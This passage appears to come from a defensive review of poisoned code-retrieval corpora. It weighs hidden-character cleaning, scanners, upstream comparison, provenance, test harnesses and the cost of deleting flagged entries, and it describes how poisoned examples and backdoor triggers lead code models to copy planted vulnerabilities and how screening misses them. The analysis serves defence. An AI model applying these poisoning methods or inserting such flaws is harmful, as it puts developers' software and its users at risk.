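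Hidden characters are a simpler problem. *RAG-Pull* (Stambolic, Dhar and Cavigelli, 2025) showed that invisible characters in public code can influence which example a retriever selects, if the model that turns text into vectors preserves them. The corpus owner should therefore remove them before indexing, not just before showing entries to a person. *Unvalidated Trust* (2025) recommends comparing the original text with the cleaned version, recording what was removed and raising an alert if the two versions differ. Silent cleaning would destroy evidence of tampering. Some hidden characters have legitimate uses, so an alert doesn't prove an attack. The check takes little work, but it wouldn't catch a poisoned entry written entirely in ordinary characters, like the published CodePoisonRAG examples.

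Most tests of automatic screening have used other kinds of poison. In *DRAINCODE* (2026), the poisoned entries made a coding assistant waste energy. Neither a standard classifier nor a measure of how well a language model predicts the text could reliably detect them. A third detector, a fine-tuned version of the code model CodeBERT, could process only 512 tokens (short pieces of text) at a time, so it checked only part of many longer entries.

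*Exploring the Security Threats of Retriever Backdoors in Retrieval-Augmented Code Generation* (2025) tested ways to detect poisoned samples in a retriever's training data. A method that groups similar samples and looks for odd groups failed when there were very few poisoned samples, because they formed no clear pattern. A filter for unusual words removed every poisoned sample from some older attacks. The paper warns that this score alone doesn't show that a filter recognized the attack, since deleting the entire dataset would score just as well.

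Rewriting every entry with a language model is an unreliable substitute for finding the poisoned ones. *Semantically-Equivalent Transformations-Based Backdoor Attacks against Neural Code Models* (2025) tested rewriting with ten models, on code containing patterns that trigger a backdoor in a trained model. Rewriting usually destroyed crudely inserted triggers, but even the best model disrupted only 48% of the subtler ones. Rewriting would probably work worse against a planted vulnerability, because a faithful rewrite keeps what the code does, including its failure to check a file name.

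### Comparing versions and tracing origins

Comparing an entry with upstream, the project it came from, is better supported by evidence than most of these checks. In *Cracks in The Stack*, Jahanshahi and Mockus (2025) applied this comparison to The Stack v2, a large public collection of code for training language models. They looked up each file's hash, a short code computed from its contents, in an archive of the histories of nearly all public projects. About 17% of the files had a newer version. In a smaller, cleaned set of 87 million files, 19,944 had a later version whose change message mentioned a known vulnerability.

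Half of the updates that the researchers dated were from June 2020 or earlier, years before the dataset came out in 2024. A corpus owner could automatically replace the outdated files and keep the useful examples. But the method depends on developers' change messages, and when the researchers checked 20 supposed bug fixes by hand, three were not clearly fixes.

A poisoned example written for an attack has no later fix to search for. Changing one character changes a file's hash, so an exact lookup won't connect an altered copy with its original. The owner would have to search for functions that do the same job and compare their security checks. In CodePoisonRAG, the clean entries and the originals of the poisoned ones came from the same collection, so a search by description might well have found both versions. An assistant could compare the examples it retrieves for each request in the same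 way, and raise an alarm if one checks the file name and another doesn't. This approach is untested, and legitimate functions often differ in this way because their callers do different things.

Provenance records make such comparisons possible, but existing ones are poor. For 62% of the files in the cleaned set that more than one project had used, the recorded origin differed from the earliest known one. Even accurate records would not show whether an entry is sound. The xz project's history correctly named Jia Tan, who had a good reputation, and "George Acosta" was a false name on a harmless patch.

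Provenance is more useful once someone has found a bad entry. If the corpus records each entry's source, contributor and hash, the owner can remove exact copies and recheck everything else from the same account. Without such records, Binarly had no way to look up every Docker Hub image built on one infected with the xz backdoor.

### Running the entry or checking the finished program

A test harness could expose some flaws that are hard to see by reading the code. For the log-download function, the harness could create a log folder and a private file outside that folder, then check whether the function ever returns the private file. The poisoned version would fail this test. The safe version relies on `securityCheck`, which is missing, so its result would depend on what the harness used instead.

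Lily did well at detecting backdoors by running code, but it had complete programs, existing harnesses and an older version for comparison. The systems in the AI Cyber Challenge could write their own test inputs, also for complete programs. It remains to be tested whether a model could write reliable harnesses for thousands of isolated functions. Each harness would also need a rule for recognizing bad behavior, and should run in a sandbox because the code may be malicious.

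A program written with the assistant's help is easier to check than a corpus, because it has callers, libraries and tests, and its developers know what it should do. Vulnerable code is also more common in such programs than poisoned entries are in a corpus. Suppose 150 of every 1,000 generated functions are vulnerable. The scanner that catches half of the flaws and flags 5% of sound code would give 75 true alarms and about 43 false ones, so nearly two in three would be right. Some of the true alarms would be for flaws that the model introduced without any poisoned example, which developers also need to fix.

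There is some direct evidence that this check is practical. Yu and colleagues ran working exploits against generated code in real projects, and the agents in Sun and colleagues' study recognized about 70% of their own memory-related flaws when asked to look for bugs. But those agents still missed about 30%, and every project that receives the poisoned example has to catch the flaw separately. The assistant should therefore record which entries it used for each answer, so that once one project confirms a flaw, the corpus owner could trace it to the example and remove that example for everyone. None of the poisoning studies measured how much this would help.

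### Dropping suspicious entries

Suspicious code is much easier to handle in a corpus than in the Linux kernel, because the corpus's owner can delete it without deciding whether it is malicious. Deleting a function from a corpus doesn't accuse anyone or break a program, whereas a false alarm about a kernel patch delays a contributor's work and takes up a maintainer's time.

The saving in labor is real, since investigating the 646 alarms in the first example would take about 54 hours at five minutes each. In the cleaned set from The Stack v2, a 5% false-alarm rate would mean more than four million alarms, too many to investigate by hand.

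But the deleted examples may have been useful. In Lin and colleagues' poisoning study, GPT-4o's code scored 0.75 for similarity to the correct function with the accurate dense retriever and a clean corpus, but only 0.18 with the keyword retriever. This gap exaggerates the value of a good example, because the corpus contained the correct function itself, and similar code isn't necessarily correct. Still, it suggests that the output depends heavily on retrieving a close match.

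Scanners would be more likely to wrongly delete sound examples that handle files, databases or memory, because they tend to flag such code. These examples can prevent flaws. If a scanner had wrongly deleted the image library's Targa reader, for example, GPT-5.4 would probably have left the zero-width check out of its GIF reader. Deleting sound examples can also move a poisoned one that the scanner missed higher in the search results.

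A rough calculation shows when deletion reduces the total number of flaws. In CodePoisonRAG, poisoning raised the rate of the chosen flaw in Code Llama's answers by 64 percentage points. The first scanner deletes about 14 clean entries for each poisoned one. If developers request all the functions equally often, deletion helps only if losing a clean entry raises the chance of a flaw by less than 64 ÷ 14, or about 4.5 points. The stronger scanner deletes only 1.6 clean entries for each poisoned one, so its limit is about 40 points.

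The harm from losing a sound example is unknown. The nearest measurement comes from Sun and colleagues' web experiment, where secure existing applications raised the share of correct and secure answers by 4.4 points. By that measure, the weaker scanner might do about as much harm as good, while the stronger one would clearly help. Current models may also copy fewer flaws than Code Llama did. If a poisoned example adds only 6.3 points, as one insecure example did in Yu and colleagues' test, the limits fall to about 0.4 and 4 points. But an attacker would probably target common requests, which would make each poisoned entry more harmful than an average clean one is useful.

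The argument that false alarms do little harm therefore holds only for an accurate scanner. An owner with a poor scanner could set flagged entries aside instead of deleting them, and have someone review one only when it would be the best match for a real request. Reviewers would then spend no time on entries that no developer needs, but the few developers who need a flagged entry would have to wait for its review.
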